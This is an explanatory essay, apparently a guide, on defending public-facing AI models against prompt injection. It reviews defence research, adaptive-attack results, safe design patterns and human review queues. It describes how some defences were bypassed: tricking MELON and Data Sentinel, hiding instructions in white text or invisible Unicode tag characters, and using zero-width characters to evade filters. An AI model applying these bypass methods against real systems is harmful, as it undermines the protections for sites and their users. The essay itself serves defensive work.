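Ordinary code can perform the first two checks. For Grokipedia, code can confirm that a source exists, but a person or a model has to judge whether it supports the claim. SpaceXAI could give this task to a separate model that sees only the proposed sentence and the relevant passage of the source. That model would be harder to persuade because it wouldn't see the contributor's arguments. Hostile text in the source could still mislead it, and so could a page that looks honest but is wrong.

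Some mistakes are serious enough to justify waiting for human review. Grokipedia could continue to accept corrected dates and spellings within minutes, but hold accusations against living people until an employee has read them. Contributors might disguise an accusation as a small correction to avoid the delay, so the software should decide what to hold by comparing the old and new text, not by relying on the contributor's description of the change.

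## Tests of delimiters, trained resistance and filters for untrusted text

Besides checking answers before publication, developers try to stop the model from obeying a stranger's text by marking the text as untrusted, training the model to give it less authority, or screening it with a second model. These defences did well when their makers tested them against known attacks. In October 2025 researchers broke 12 of them by adapting the attack to each defence, with success rates above 90% against most.

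### Marking the text

Spotlighting changes untrusted text to signal its source to the model. *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting* (2024) describes three versions. Suppose the library's assistant has to summarise a reader's review that begins "Lovely book".

| Version | What the model might receive |
|---|---|
| Delimiting | `<<Lovely book>>` |
| Marking | `Lovely^book` |
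| Encoding | `TG92ZWx5IGJvb2s=` |

The system prompt explains the change and tells the model not to follow instructions in the changed text. With delimiting, a reviewer who guesses the closing symbols can type them, then add an instruction that appears to be outside the review. The developer can prevent this by choosing random symbols for each request. Marking puts a symbol between all the words, so every part of the review shows its origin. Encoded text (base64 in this example) looks nothing like an instruction, but the model has to decode it, and a weaker model may make mistakes.

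In the 2024 work, spotlighting significantly reduced the success of attacks without spoiling the model's answers. But the review is still part of the model's input, and nothing guarantees that the model will follow the explanation in the system prompt. Simple tags had mixed results in the plugin study.

A related method, prompt sandwiching, repeats the user's request after the untrusted text, so that the model reads the real task last.

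### Training the model

Model companies can also train a model to rank instructions by their source. *The Instruction Hierarchy* (2024) compares the models of the time to an operating system that runs every program in kernel mode, where each has full control of the machine. It proposes training the model to follow the more privileged instruction when two conflict. For example, if the library's system prompt limits the assistant to questions about computers, the model should refuse to write a casino advertisement.

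The first version of the instruction hierarchy had three levels and used artificial examples of conflicts to train GPT-3.5, according to *Training LLMs to Enforce Multi-Level Instruction Hierarchies via Gravity-Weighted Direct Preference Optimization* (2026). The paper found no published method that used more than three or four levels, or that penalised serious violations more than trivial ones.

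The training also gives a stranger's text more influence when it arrives under the wrong label, as *When Context Gets Root* (2026) points out and the plugin study showed.

*StruQ* (2024) proposed giving the model two fields, one for the instruction and one for data. On the library's site, the first might contain "Summarise this review" and the second the review itself, including a line that asks for a poem. The training examples include stray commands like this, and the correct answer is always the summary. Special delimiters separate the fields, and ordinary code removes them from the review so that its author can't fake the boundary. Unlike a database placeholder, the boundary only works if the model has learnt to ignore commands in the data field.

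*SecAlign* (2024) kept the two fields but trained the model on pairs of answers. In the library's case, one answer would summarise the review, the other would be the poem, and training would favour the summary.

StruQ and SecAlign both reduced the success rate of handwritten attacks to nearly zero, according to *May I have your Attention?* (2025). In a harder test, a program repeatedly alters the hostile text to make the attacker's intended response more likely. These optimised attacks succeeded 89% and 97% of the time on two undefended models. StruQ remained vulnerable, while SecAlign cut the success rate to less than a quarter of StruQ's.

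Later tests were less favourable. *A Critical Evaluation of Defenses against Prompt Injection Attacks* (2025) found that some attacks on a StruQ model succeeded 7 to 16% of the time and others 92 to 100%. It also found that both methods made the model somewhat less useful, contrary to the original claims. A site that rents a commercial model usually can't apply either method, so it depends on whatever training the model's maker has done.

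### Screening the input

An input classifier is a separate program that labels text as safe or hostile before the main model acts on it. Most are small language models trained on examples of attacks and harmless text. A site can add one without changing its main model.

The classifier has little context, so it can block honest questions and miss attacks. If a visitor to the library pastes in a suspicious message and asks whether it is a prompt injection, the classifier may block the question because it contains an attack. A hostile review might present its demand as a routine office procedure, and the classifier may let it through because it has no information about the library's procedures. A stricter classifier will catch more of these reviews but also block more honest questions.

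### Twelve defences against attackers who adapt

*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested all these approaches except the original instruction hierarchy. Some of the researchers worked for OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, which sell models with similar protections.

The researchers attacked each defence in a loop. The attacker proposed a hostile text, checked how the defended system responded, then kept and revised the most promising texts. The researchers ran this loop in four ways. The first used the model's internal calculations to choose better words. The second trained an attacking model by reinforcement learning, which rewards it for successful attacks. In the third, a language model rewrote earlier attempts and a program selected the best. The fourth relied on people.

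The researchers tested eight of the defences against the rewriting method in AgentDojo, which simulates tasks such as handling email or Slack messages for assistants with tools. They allowed up to 800 tries in each of 80 scenarios. The table compares the results with those of a fixed attack supplied with AgentDojo. The main model was Gemini 2.5 Pro in every row except the last, which covers Meta SecAlign, because that defence is itself a model.

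| Defence | Ordinary tasks completed | Fixed attack succeeded | Adapted attack succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 74% | 30% | 100% |
| Spotlighting | 75% | 28% | 99% |
| Prompt sandwiching | 73% | 21% | 95% |
| Protect AI (classifier) | 39% | 15% | 90% |
| PIGuard (classifier) | 39% | 0% | 71% |
| PromptGuard (classifier) | 72% | 26% | 94% |
| Model Armor (classifier) | 59% | 28% | 90% |
| MELON | 58% | 0% | 89% |
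| Meta SecAlign | 73% | 5% | 96% |

When the adapted attack worked, it typically took between 13 and 46 tries, few enough for a person to type in an afternoon. PIGuard resisted the attack best, but the assistant completed barely half as many ordinary tasks with it as without it. If a site sends flagged messages to a reviewer instead of blocking them, the reviewer has to sort out the ones flagged by mistake.

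MELON runs the model a second time with the user's request replaced by a request for a summary. It flags any tool call the model makes both times, because that call must have come from the untrusted text. The attacker got past this by telling the model to act only if its task was something other than summarising. On another model, Llama 3.3, this raised the attack's success rate from 76% to 95%.

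The remaining four defences were tested against the attacking model trained by reinforcement learning. It succeeded against StruQ in every case tested, often by imitating a system prompt. RPO and Circuit Breakers are meant to stop jailbreaks, in which users try to get harmful material that the model's maker forbids. The attacker beat RPO in 98% of cases and Circuit Breakers in 100%. Data Sentinel instructs a model to repeat a secret word while ignoring the untrusted text, and treats a failure as a sign of injection. The attacker avoided detection by redefining the task. For example, it described sentiment as a clue to whether a message was spam, and the model sorted messages into spam and normal instead of positive and negative.

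The researchers describe prompt-based defences as no better than no defence, but with GPT-5 Mini as the main model, spotlighting reduced the adapted attack's success from 75% to 47%. Results varied a lot between runs, and the researchers expected that a larger budget would break GPT-5 Mini too. Even so, a developer who can add spotlighting in a few lines has some reason to do so.

### People as attackers

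More than 500 people competed for $20,000 in prizes across 40 challenges based on AgentDojo. Each challenge combined a model and a task, and some included a defence that contestants hadn't been told about. Contestants wrote hostile text, watched the assistant's reasoning and tool calls, and tried again. At least one contestant succeeded in each challenge. Contestants produced 265 successful attacks on spotlighting and 178 on prompt sandwiching.

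Nasr and colleagues compared people with the automated search in 29 scenarios that both attempted. At least one person succeeded in every scenario, while the search succeeded in 69%. The best individual who tried all 29 succeeded in 75%. Much of the human advantage therefore came from having many people try different ideas, as also happens with a popular public chatbot.

The share of individual submissions that succeeded was much lower. For Gemini 2.5 Pro with extended reasoning, it was 11.1% without MELON and 0.4% with it. For Gemini 2.5 Flash, it was 28.8% without spotlighting and 43.7% with it. Different people made different numbers of submissions to each challenge, so these rates don't show how well the defences work.

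The contestants and the search also had more information than an ordinary visitor would. The search received the classifiers' confidence scores. A visitor to a public assistant normally sees only the reply, and someone who plants a review has to question the assistant to see whether it worked. Limited feedback slows an attacker down, but some of these classifiers are free to download, so an attacker can practise on a copy. The researchers tested whether each defence could be broken at all and didn't try to measure how much effort a real attacker would spend. They still consider classifiers useful against unskilled attackers.

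### Why a fixed test set overstates safety

With no defence in place, the fixed attack never succeeded against GPT-5 Mini, but the adapted attack succeeded in 75% of the same scenarios. A developer who ran only the fixed attack would have concluded that the model needed no protection.

A fixed test uses attacks written before the defence existed. The defence's makers can train on those attacks or similar ones, so a good score may mean only that the model recognises them. An attacker who sees a text fail will change it. In most uses of machine learning, by contrast, new data usually resembles past data, and nobody chooses it to cause errors.

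Researchers keep using fixed tests because they require few resources and are easy to repeat. *Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (2026) ran fixed attacks on 420 cases but adaptive ones on only 40, because running every adaptive attack on all the cases would have required too many resources. The 40 came from cases already known to be vulnerable, so the adaptive attacks look stronger than they would on the full set.

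Even a thorough adaptive test can't prove that a defence is safe, because a better-funded or more inventive group may succeed where the testers failed. Developers could do the easiest part of such a test themselves by spending a day trying to break their own assistant before launch, as Nasr and colleagues advise researchers to do with a new defence.

### The arithmetic of repeated tries

A success rate means little without the number of attempts, because an attacker can keep trying, as with repeated suggestions to Grokipedia. If each attempt has a 1% chance of success and attempts are independent, the chance that at least one of 100 succeeds is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%. If a better model lowers the chance per attempt to 0.1%, the attacker needs about 1,000 attempts to have the same 63% chance. A program can make that many overnight if the site doesn't limit them.

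Real attempts aren't independent. In February 2026 Anthropic published prompt injection success rates for Claude Opus 4.6, a model since superseded, in different settings and with different numbers of attempts. VentureBeat reports that when the model operated a computer through its screen without extra safeguards, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. If attempts were independent, eight would have reached 79%. It took 200 to reach 78.6%, presumably because some scenarios were easy and others very hard. Extra safeguards lowered the rate for 200 attempts to 57.1%.

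The setting made an even larger difference. In a restricted coding environment, all 200 attempts against the same model failed, even without safeguards. A single resistance rate for the model would not show this difference, so a site owner should look for the rate from the test closest to the planned use.

### Current models

The newest detailed measurements come from Google DeepMind's *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (Kurakin, Karande and colleagues, 2026), which used 16 AI agents working in pairs. The agents shared notes and a list of the best attempts, and together had up to 320 tries in each of 100 scenarios. In one scenario, a user asked an assistant to book a tutoring session, and hostile text in the booking system's response was meant to make the assistant record blood pressure readings. The attack counted as a success only if the assistant used the right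 tool with almost exactly the right details.

The researchers turned off Google's defences outside the model. With Gemini 4 Argon as the attacker, the agents broke these shares of the scenarios:

| Model under attack | Within 150 tries | Within 320 tries |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Argon | 13% | 34% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 66% | 90% |
| Gemini 3.7 Flash | 69% | 94% |
| Gemini 3.6 Flash | 97% | 99% |
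| Kimi K3 | 95% | 99% |
| GLM-5.3 | 99% | 99% |
| DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash | 99% | 99% |

Resistance to prompt injection depends heavily on the model. A small site that picks a fast, cheap model or a free one may get much weaker resistance than its owner would expect from headlines about the best models.

With 320 tries, the agents broke 34% of the scenarios on Gemini 4 Argon. A constant rate of success would have produced about 26%, so later tries were more productive, probably because the agents learnt from their failures and from each other. Weaker Gemini models, given the same 150 tries, broke almost none of these scenarios. A model that resists today's attackers may therefore be vulnerable to the next generation of attackers.

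These rates are probably higher than those for serious harm, because the researchers chose harmless actions to measure whether a model would follow instructions in a tool's response at all. A model might record someone's blood pressure on a stranger's instruction and still refuse to email a password. The tests also covered assistants with tools, and an attacker has less to gain from a chatbot that only answers questions.

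In a smaller test with Google's external defences switched on, a weaker attacker succeeded in 6 of 80 AgentDojo scenarios on Gemini 3.6 Flash within 25 tries. The results are not directly comparable with those of the larger test because the attacker, scenarios and budget were different.

Human attackers had been succeeding less often against the newest models. Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026) studied indirect injection in a public competition that the security company Gray Swan ran with OpenAI, Anthropic, Meta and government institutes from Britain and the United States. Contestants had to hijack an assistant without its user noticing. *Your AI Agent Can Be Compromised. You'd Never Know* (Dziemian, 2026) reports that 464 people made more than 272,000 attacks on 13 models, and that every model sometimes failed. Kurakin and colleagues report that by autumn, attacks saved from the competition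 worked less than 1% of the time on recent Gemini models and some versions of Claude. But the saved attacks are another fixed test set, and the agents' new attacks still succeeded.

TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that OpenAI's tests found low failure rates when the user typed the attack, as in ordinary chat, and higher ones when it arrived through tools or outside content. The plugin study similarly found that typed attacks rarely moved an assistant with a strict system prompt off its subject.

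Patient attackers can do better in chat too. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) describes an automated attacker that tried to extract protected information from chatbots in campaigns of 500 rounds. The strongest defences that relied on the model held for 247 to 277 rounds, then failed. With a filter on outgoing replies, nothing leaked in 15,000 attacks. Such a filter suits a secret the developer can describe in advance, like an access code, though it is better still not to give a public assistant the secret. A filter that recognises every false statement about the library's opening hours would be much harder to write.

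### Designs that limit a hijacked model

Models still follow hostile text some of the time, so a developer can design the assistant to limit what an attack can achieve. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes six ways to do this. All six follow the rule that once a model has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any harmful action.

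| Pattern | What it guarantees | What it costs |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector: the model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results | Text in the results can't steer the model | The assistant can't do anything the developer didn't foresee |
| Plan then execute: the model lists its actions before reading outside text | Outside text can't add an action, though it can change what an action contains | The assistant can't change course after reading something |
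| Map-reduce: a separate model reads each document and gives a restricted answer | A hostile document affects only its own answer | The task has to divide into separate documents |
| Dual LLM: one model uses tools, and another without tools reads the untrusted text | The model with tools never reads that text | The system is harder to build, and the reader can still return false information |
| Code then execute: the model writes a program before reading outside text | The text can't change the program's steps | The model has to foresee every step, and hostile text can still alter the contents |
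| Context minimisation: the software removes the visitor's words before the model writes the reply | Those words can't directly steer the reply | The reply can't adapt to how the visitor asked |

If a library member asks for an email listing their current loans, a model using the plan-then-execute pattern sets its steps (read the loans, then email them to the member) before it sees any loan records. A hostile note in a record could put a false warning in the email, but could not change the recipient if the plan fixes the address. The pattern doesn't protect against instructions in the member's own request, because the model reads the request before making the plan.

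Nasr and colleagues left such designs out of their tests because the attack was certain to fail in most of their scenarios. They add that these designs suit only some tasks. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) tested Progent, another defence that works outside the model. Standard attacks succeeded 4.2% of the time and adapted ones 2.6%. The result is encouraging, but according to the paper, its single handwritten attack may have been weak.

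### A customer service chatbot

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues apply the patterns to a furniture shop's chatbot that answers questions, files returns and cancels orders. They assume its knowledge base contains only the shop's own text, so the main danger is the customer's message. That assumption was wrong for some shops in the plugin study.

An attacker could persuade a customer to paste in a hostile prompt that makes the chatbot look up the customer's data and put it in a link or image address. Someone could also publish a screenshot of something embarrassing they got the chatbot to write.

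The simplest design adds a classifier that rejects messages unrelated to furniture. It wrongly refuses a few legitimate questions but otherwise leaves the chatbot as useful as before. However, it makes one decision about the whole message, so if an attacker asks about a sofa and then makes an unrelated request, it may accept both.

An action selector is stricter. The developer writes a list of acceptable requests, and the software carries out the one closest in meaning to the customer's message. A hostile message can at worst trigger the wrong item on the list, and every item should be safe. Returns and cancellations still need an identity check, or a visitor could cancel someone else's order. The chatbot also turns away customers with reasonable questions that the developer didn't expect. The library could similarly have its chatbot choose from 200 answers that librarians have checked, and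 pass unmatched questions to a librarian.

With context minimisation, the chatbot can still write its own replies. If a customer asks for the price of a sofa and adds an instruction to offer a huge discount, the model first turns the message into a database query. The software then deletes the message, and the model writes the reply from the query and its result. Deleting the message removes the instruction, but it would also remove an honest request for a one-sentence answer. The query also has to follow a strict format, such as a product number and the word "price", or part of the hostile instruction may survive in it.

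### A recommender that reads reviews

The product recommender has to read strangers' text because it summarises what buyers think of a product. If one model reads all the reviews together, an instruction in one review can make it praise that product or criticise a rival.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues first consider making the model quote a review for each advantage and drawback. Customers could then check the claims, but few will want to read and count the quotations. Customers also couldn't see why the model had left out another toaster, so a hostile review could harm a rival product without being detected.

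The map-reduce design gives each review to a separate model, which can only mark fixed categories such as "good price" or "easy to use". Ordinary code then adds up the marks for each toaster. A hostile review can make the model mark every favourable category, but a fake review full of praise could do the same without prompt injection. The hostile review can't change how the system reads other reviews or rates other products. The shop still has to deal with fake reviews, and people who submit hundreds of them can distort the totals.

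This protection loses any detail that falls outside the chosen categories. If nobody included a category for thick slices of bread, the recommender can't answer a customer who asks whether they fit, even if 20 buyers mentioned it. The developer can have a model suggest categories before it reads any reviews, which helps with common questions, but a customer with an unusual question will have to read the reviews.

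## Human review of public submissions: Wikipedia, curl and AISafety.info

Many of these designs pass the difficult cases to a person, such as the librarian who answers questions the chatbot can't match to a checked answer. This works only if the person can keep up with the submissions. On the English Wikipedia, volunteers never sorted about five-sixths of the comments that readers sent through an open form. The maintainers of curl, a widely used program for transferring data, spent much of 2025 disproving security reports that people had written with AI and not checked.

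### Wikipedia's comment box

Almost anyone can edit Wikipedia, but few readers do. The Wikimedia Foundation, the non-profit that runs the site, tried to involve more of them with its Article Feedback Tool. An earlier version asked readers to rate an article with stars. Version 5, which the Foundation began developing in November 2011, asked whether they had found what they were looking for and provided a comment box. The Foundation's *Article feedback/Version 5* explains the change with an example. Unlike a three-star rating, a reader's comment that a biography has no section on the person's childhood tells an editor what to add.

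Comments went straight onto a public feedback page for each article. Volunteers could then mark them as useful, resolved or inappropriate, or hide them.

From July 2012 the form appeared on a random tenth of English Wikipedia articles, about 400,000. That autumn readers submitted about 4,100 posts a day, according to the project's slides, *Article Feedback v5* (2013). About 90 volunteers a day helped sort them, dealing with 3.5% within 24 hours and 11.5% within a month, or roughly five posts per volunteer per day.

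The Foundation expected more than 30,000 posts a day if it put the form on every article, according to *Article Feedback tool faces community resistance* (The ed17, 2013), an article in Wikipedia's volunteer newspaper. The same 90 people would each have had to sort over 300 posts a day. The comments were easy to read, at an average of 23 words, but one editor, GregJackP, complained that even a good one was typically a question that somebody would have to research.

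### How many comments were useful

The Foundation had 18 volunteers assess a sample of the comments, with two people judging each one separately. A comment counted as useful if it suggested something to be done to the article. According to the researcher Aaron Halfaker, who explained the method in the discussion below The ed17's article, 66% of the comments were judged useful by at least one person and 39% by both. The two judges therefore disagreed about more than a quarter of the comments.

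The Foundation had invited people who had recently sorted more than ten comments, and they may have liked the tool more than most editors did. Another editor, Peter Southwood, read about 200 comments from a separate random sample and thought closer to 10% were useful.

Wikimedia Foundation's *Article feedback/Version 5/Report* gives a third estimate, based on the volunteers' everyday sorting. It puts the useful share at 12% on average across the English, French and German sites. The English figure in that average is about 10%, because volunteers marked 65,000 of 672,000 comments as useful or resolved. But they never reviewed 560,000 of the comments, and the 10% counts all of those as useless. More than half of the comments they did review were useful or resolved, but that probably overstates the share for all comments, because volunteers may have picked out the promising ones.

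The French results are a better guide. Volunteers on the French site sorted three-quarters of 223,000 comments and marked 15% of the sorted comments as useful or resolved. French editors may simply have been stricter. Readers can check this in the *Wikipedia Article Feedback corpus*, an archive of about 1.5 million messages from the three sites.

### What the filters could stop

Software filters rejected about 10% of feedback before it appeared, according to Wikimedia Foundation's *Article feedback/Version 5/Feature Requirements*. The filters compared each comment with patterns that volunteers had written, many adapted from the rules that already checked article edits. A filter could reject a comment, warn its author, or accept the comment and flag it for review. On the English site, every match led to rejection, as a developer noted in Wikimedia Phabricator's *Identify which filters triggered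 auto-flag actions*, an entry in the project's bug tracker. A reader whose legitimate comment matched a pattern had to reword it or give up, and the rejected comment never reached the volunteers' review queue.

The Foundation recommended filters for obscenities, contact details, advertising, gibberish and program code. A rule against code suits an encyclopedia's comment box, but it would stop the library's visitor from asking about `<b>`. The Foundation said the filter for obscenities and vandalism didn't work very well. Readers could also flag a comment as abuse, and five flags hid it automatically. The developers later realised that a group of trolls could use this to hide comments they disliked, so they added a way for trusted editors to clear the flags.

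Pattern matching cannot identify which comments would improve an article. Across the three sites, volunteers marked 17% of comments as inappropriate and 46% as needing no action, a label for praise, duplicates and remarks too vague to use. Most of the unhelpful comments were harmless, so volunteers would still have had much of the reviewing to do even with better abuse filters.

The developers also planned for emergencies, including suicide notes left as feedback. At the rate volunteers were working, such a message would probably have gone unread for at least a month. A site with an open form should say next to it how often someone reads the submissions and where to get urgent help.

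### The vote against the tool

In January 2013 the editor MZMcBride opened a formal discussion about the tool. He had complained that the Foundation introduced it without protection against abuse, and wanted it only on articles whose editors had asked for it. GregJackP proposed removing it altogether, and his view got more than twice as much support as any other. About 175 editors took part, and 63% opposed wide use.

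According to The Signpost's *Technology report* (2013), the Foundation dropped its plan for a full release that March and kept the form for articles that editors chose. The argument continued, with editors turning the form on for 3,677 articles and opponents turning it off on thousands. German editors had also voted against it, and in a French poll in January 2014, 45% wanted it removed everywhere and 38% to keep it as an option. The Foundation removed it from the English and French sites on 3 March 2014.

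The Foundation still thought the tool had worked for readers. In its survey, 70% of respondents liked it. Of the people invited to register after commenting, 2.7% did, and 3% of those invited to edit completed an edit. Some of them might have joined anyway, but on a site with so many readers, even a small percentage could bring in many new editors. The Foundation also objected that a few hundred editors had voted down something that could have helped hundreds of millions of readers, who had no real say.

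That is a fair complaint about the vote, but the readers weren't going to sort the comments. Oliver Keyes, the Foundation's liaison with the editors, argued that nobody had to sort everything, because Wikipedia accepts that some bad edits slip through and could accept the same with comments. Comments do less harm than edits, since they don't change the article. But few editors visit the page where they appear, so a libel there can stay up longer.

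The developers had considered archiving unsorted comments automatically, after two days on the busiest pages and a year on the quietest. Editors could then have sorted a few comments at a time without feeling they had to finish the queue. One lesson the team recorded was "Nobody likes a pile of homework". By 2014 the team had no resources to develop the tool further.

### Rewards for reports to curl

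Unlike Wikipedia's readers, who had nothing to gain from a useless comment, people who sent security reports to curl could hope to be paid. The project began paying for reports of genuine vulnerabilities through HackerOne in 2019. By January 2026 it had confirmed 87 vulnerabilities and paid more than $100,000, according to *The end of the curl bug-bounty* (2026), a post by curl's lead developer, Daniel Stenberg.

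The share of reports that described real vulnerabilities fell from more than 15% in earlier years to below 5% in 2025. Stenberg blamed the many AI-written junk reports, a decline in the quality of the other reports (whose authors had perhaps also trusted an AI), and people who would argue at length that a trivial finding was critical but wouldn't help to fix it. A maintainer may need hours to disprove an invented vulnerability that took a few minutes to generate, because a convincing report names real functions and describes a plausible attack.

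The project stopped paying rewards at the end of January 2026. Stenberg suspected that money was a large part of the problem, but other open-source projects that paid rewards, including Ruby, Node and Rails, had seen no comparable rise. He considered charging a small fee to submit a report but decided against it, because international payments and refunds would create more work and the fee would keep out some people with genuine findings.

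A ban on AI-written reports would also have excluded good ones. Stenberg knew of more than a hundred AI-assisted reports that had led to corrections, according to *curl Removes Bug Bounties*. Instead, curl promised to ban and publicly ridicule anyone who sent junk. This may deter a researcher with a reputation to protect, but most people who report to curl are first-time reporters and many use pseudonyms, so they can return under another name.

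The project had no such trouble with pull requests, in which people propose changes to its code. About 200 automated jobs test each change, and the maintainers needn't look at it until it passes. Contributors therefore have to produce working code before they take up the maintainers' time, whereas a fluent but false report takes little effort to send.

### Better reports, and more of them

When curl ended the payments, it also moved its reporting from HackerOne to GitHub. Two weeks later, fewer reports were arriving, but Stenberg cautioned in his weekly email of 12 February 2026 that the drop might be temporary and that some junk had already reached the new inbox. By the end of the month he had called the move to GitHub a mistake, in *curl security moves again* (2026), and in March the project returned to HackerOne without the rewards.

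In April, Stenberg (2026) declared the junk problem over in a post titled *High-Quality Chaos*. The share of confirmed vulnerabilities had returned to about 15 or 16%, the number of reports had doubled, and almost every report now showed signs of AI. According to Stenberg's weekly email of 11 April 2026, curl received seven reports in one April week, including one real vulnerability, and most of the others in that period described ordinary bugs or unclear documentation.

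It's unclear how much of the improvement came from ending the rewards, because curl also changed its reporting platform twice in the same few weeks and the AI tools were getting better. Maintainers of the Linux kernel, Firefox, Django and other projects told Stenberg that they had seen the same trend, which a change in curl's own rules can't explain. Ending the payments may have stopped some of the people who were sending junk for money, but it didn't reduce the workload for long, since the number of reports kept increasing.

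A higher share of valid reports didn't make the queue easier to handle either. Suppose curl received 100 reports in part of 2025, of which 5 were valid, and 200 in the same part of 2026, of which 30 were valid. The maintainers would have six times as many vulnerabilities to repair, and they would also have 170 reports to reject instead of 95. In *The pressure*, published in May, Willison (2026) quoted Stenberg as saying that curl was getting more than one report a day, four to five times the 2024 rate, and that the reports were typically detailed and long. Maintainers can dismiss obvious nonsense quickly, but they have to answer a careful report properly even when it turns out not to describe a vulnerability.

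By autumn the main maintainers were close to their limit. The 14 October release fixed 22 vulnerabilities, as Stenberg announced in *Twenty-two pending curl vulnerabilities*. Since 26 October, curl has required people to report minor and moderate vulnerabilities in public, where anyone can help assess and fix them. *Scrutinize our assessments* and the posts around it explain the change. More than 90% of submissions in recent years had fallen below the two most serious grades, so most of the work could be done in public. The project accepts that attackers will have slightly longer to exploit these flaws before a fix is released.

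A help desk couldn't copy that arrangement, because its visitors' messages may contain personal details. It could copy some of Stenberg's advice to people who report vulnerabilities. He asks them to open with a short explanation in their own words and to include a program that reproduces the fault. Both requests move work from the few people who read reports to the many who send them. A library's form could ask visitors which page they were on and what they had already tried. Each extra question will put off some honest visitors, particularly beginners, so the form shouldn't ask for anything the librarians won't use.

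### Edited answers and live ones

AISafety.info, a website that explains the risks of advanced AI to the public, avoids part of this problem by keeping its articles separate from its chatbot's answers. Volunteers and editors write the articles, which each answer one question. The chatbot, Stampy, replies to visitors immediately, drawing on a collection of writing about AI safety and citing its sources.

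A visitor who can't find a question on the site can suggest it. The suggestion joins the editors' list, and a page appears only after somebody has written an answer and an editor has approved it. The visitor's wording isn't published unless an editor copies it. If someone submits a casino advertisement, it goes only to that list, where editors can delete or ignore it. The chatbot's replies don't become articles, so a visitor who gets the chatbot to write something false doesn't change what other readers see.

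The editors also don't have to answer every question on their list. If 50 people ask the same thing, one article serves them all, and leaving a question unanswered doesn't harm other readers. Visitors with unusual questions may never get an edited answer, but they can ask the chatbot. The separation depends on readers noticing whether an answer was edited or came from the chatbot, so the two kinds need different labels as well as different pages.

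The chatbot still reads text from outside. Its collection has included posts from LessWrong, a forum where anyone can open an account but moderators check a newcomer's first contributions before they appear. Similarly, WordPress by default holds a comment until its author has had an earlier one approved.

Holding first posts for review concentrates the reviewers' effort on strangers, who send most of the spam, and lets regular contributors post without waiting. A spammer can get around it by posting one polite remark and advertising in the next post. A forum can make this harder by holding each newcomer's first few posts, as well as any post with several links, whoever wrote it. The method also needs accounts, so that the forum can recognise returning contributors. About 98% of the people who commented through Wikipedia's form were anonymous, so all their posts would have been held as first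 posts.

### Text that a reviewer cannot see

A reviewer can judge only visible text, but a model may also receive hidden text. The simplest way to hide text is to make it white on a white background. In July 2025 the newspaper Nikkei reported that it had found 17 research papers containing hidden instructions to AI reviewers, such as to give only praise, in white or extremely small type. A reader would have seen a blank margin, but software that copies text out of a document normally ignores its colour and size. In HTML, an attacker can also hide text in comments, in elements that the page's style rules hide, and in image descriptions.

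Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character, allows a subtler version. It includes invisible "tag" characters that correspond to the ordinary Latin letters, digits and punctuation. The letter b is U+0062, for instance, and its invisible counterpart is U+E0062. Riley Goodside, who had helped to publicise prompt injection in 2022, showed in 2024 that ChatGPT could read instructions written in these characters. A stranger could add a paragraph of them to a question about library cards, and a librarian would not notice them when reading and approving the question, or even when copying it into another document.

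Zero-width characters, which are also invisible, can hide a word from a filter. If a spammer puts one after the s in "casino", a filter that searches for "casino" won't find it. The word looks the same to a reader, and a model will often still recognise it.

Normalising text means converting different encodings of the same content to one standard form. Unicode defines several such forms. NFKC turns wide or decorative letters into plain ones, which helps a filter, but it also turns "What is 5²?" into "What is 52?". It doesn't remove invisible tag characters or convert a Russian а to the Latin letter that looks identical. A milder form, NFC, leaves 5² unchanged, so a site can store the text in NFC and give the filter a separate NFKC copy.

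The site then has to deal with the invisible characters. Deleting all of them would damage honest messages, because Persian spelling uses one zero-width character, many emoji use another to join their parts, and the flags of England, Scotland and Wales contain tag characters. A help desk can safely delete tag characters outside those flags. For the rest, it can make them visible to the reviewer with a function like this:

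```
function showHidden(text) {
  return text.replace(/\p{Default_Ignorable_Code_Point}/gu,
    (c) => "[U+" + c.codePointAt(0).toString(16).toUpperCase() + "]");
}
```

The long name in the pattern is Unicode's own category for characters that normally display nothing. If somebody has put a zero-width space after the tag in the library's usual question, the reviewer sees:

`What does <b>[U+200B] do?`

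One or two such codes usually come from an emoji or a careless copy and paste, but a row of 200 is a hidden message. The page must escape the result before displaying it, like any other text in a staff log.

Reviewers and the model should work from the same text. The server can extract and normalise each submission once, save the result beside the original, show it to the reviewer as plain text, and send the same characters to the model. White text then appears in black. If a visitor uploads a document, the reviewer should see the extracted words next to the picture of the page, because the picture alone may not show all the text the model will read. Approval should apply only to that saved version. If the author edits the submission, or it depends on a web page whose contents can change, it needs another review.

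Reviewers can also miss text hidden in a long message. The form field used to attack Salesforce's assistant allowed sales enquiries so long that hardly anyone would read a full one carefully. Wikipedia's form allowed 5,000 characters, although the average comment had only 113. A limit of 500 characters would suit most questions to a library and let a reviewer see the whole message without scrolling.

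### What a filter leaves for the reviewers

Suppose, as an illustration, that the library receives 1,000 submissions in a month and 20 of them are attacks. It has a filter that catches 95% of attacks and wrongly flags 2% of everything else. The filter sorts the submissions like this:

| | Flagged | Not flagged | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Attacks | 19 | 1 | 20 |
| Honest submissions | about 20 | about 960 | 980 |
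| Total | about 39 | about 961 | 1,000 |

The librarians get 39 items to review, half of them harmless, and one attack gets through. At two minutes an item, the review takes about 80 minutes, compared with 33 hours to read everything.

Half the flagged items are harmless, even though the filter wrongly flags only 2% of honest submissions, because honest submissions far outnumber attacks. If there were only 2 attacks among the 1,000, the same filter would flag about 22 items, about 20 of them harmless. A librarian who has approved ten harmless items in a row is likely to read the eleventh less carefully. If the librarians wrongly approve one in ten of the 19 attacks they see, about two more attacks reach the public, for a total of about three instead of one.

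The 95% catch rate is the least reliable number here, since attackers who adapted their text got past most of the classifiers researchers tested. If it fell to 10%, 18 attacks would get through and the librarians' queue would shrink to about 22 items. Someone who looked only at the queue's length might conclude that attacks had become rarer.

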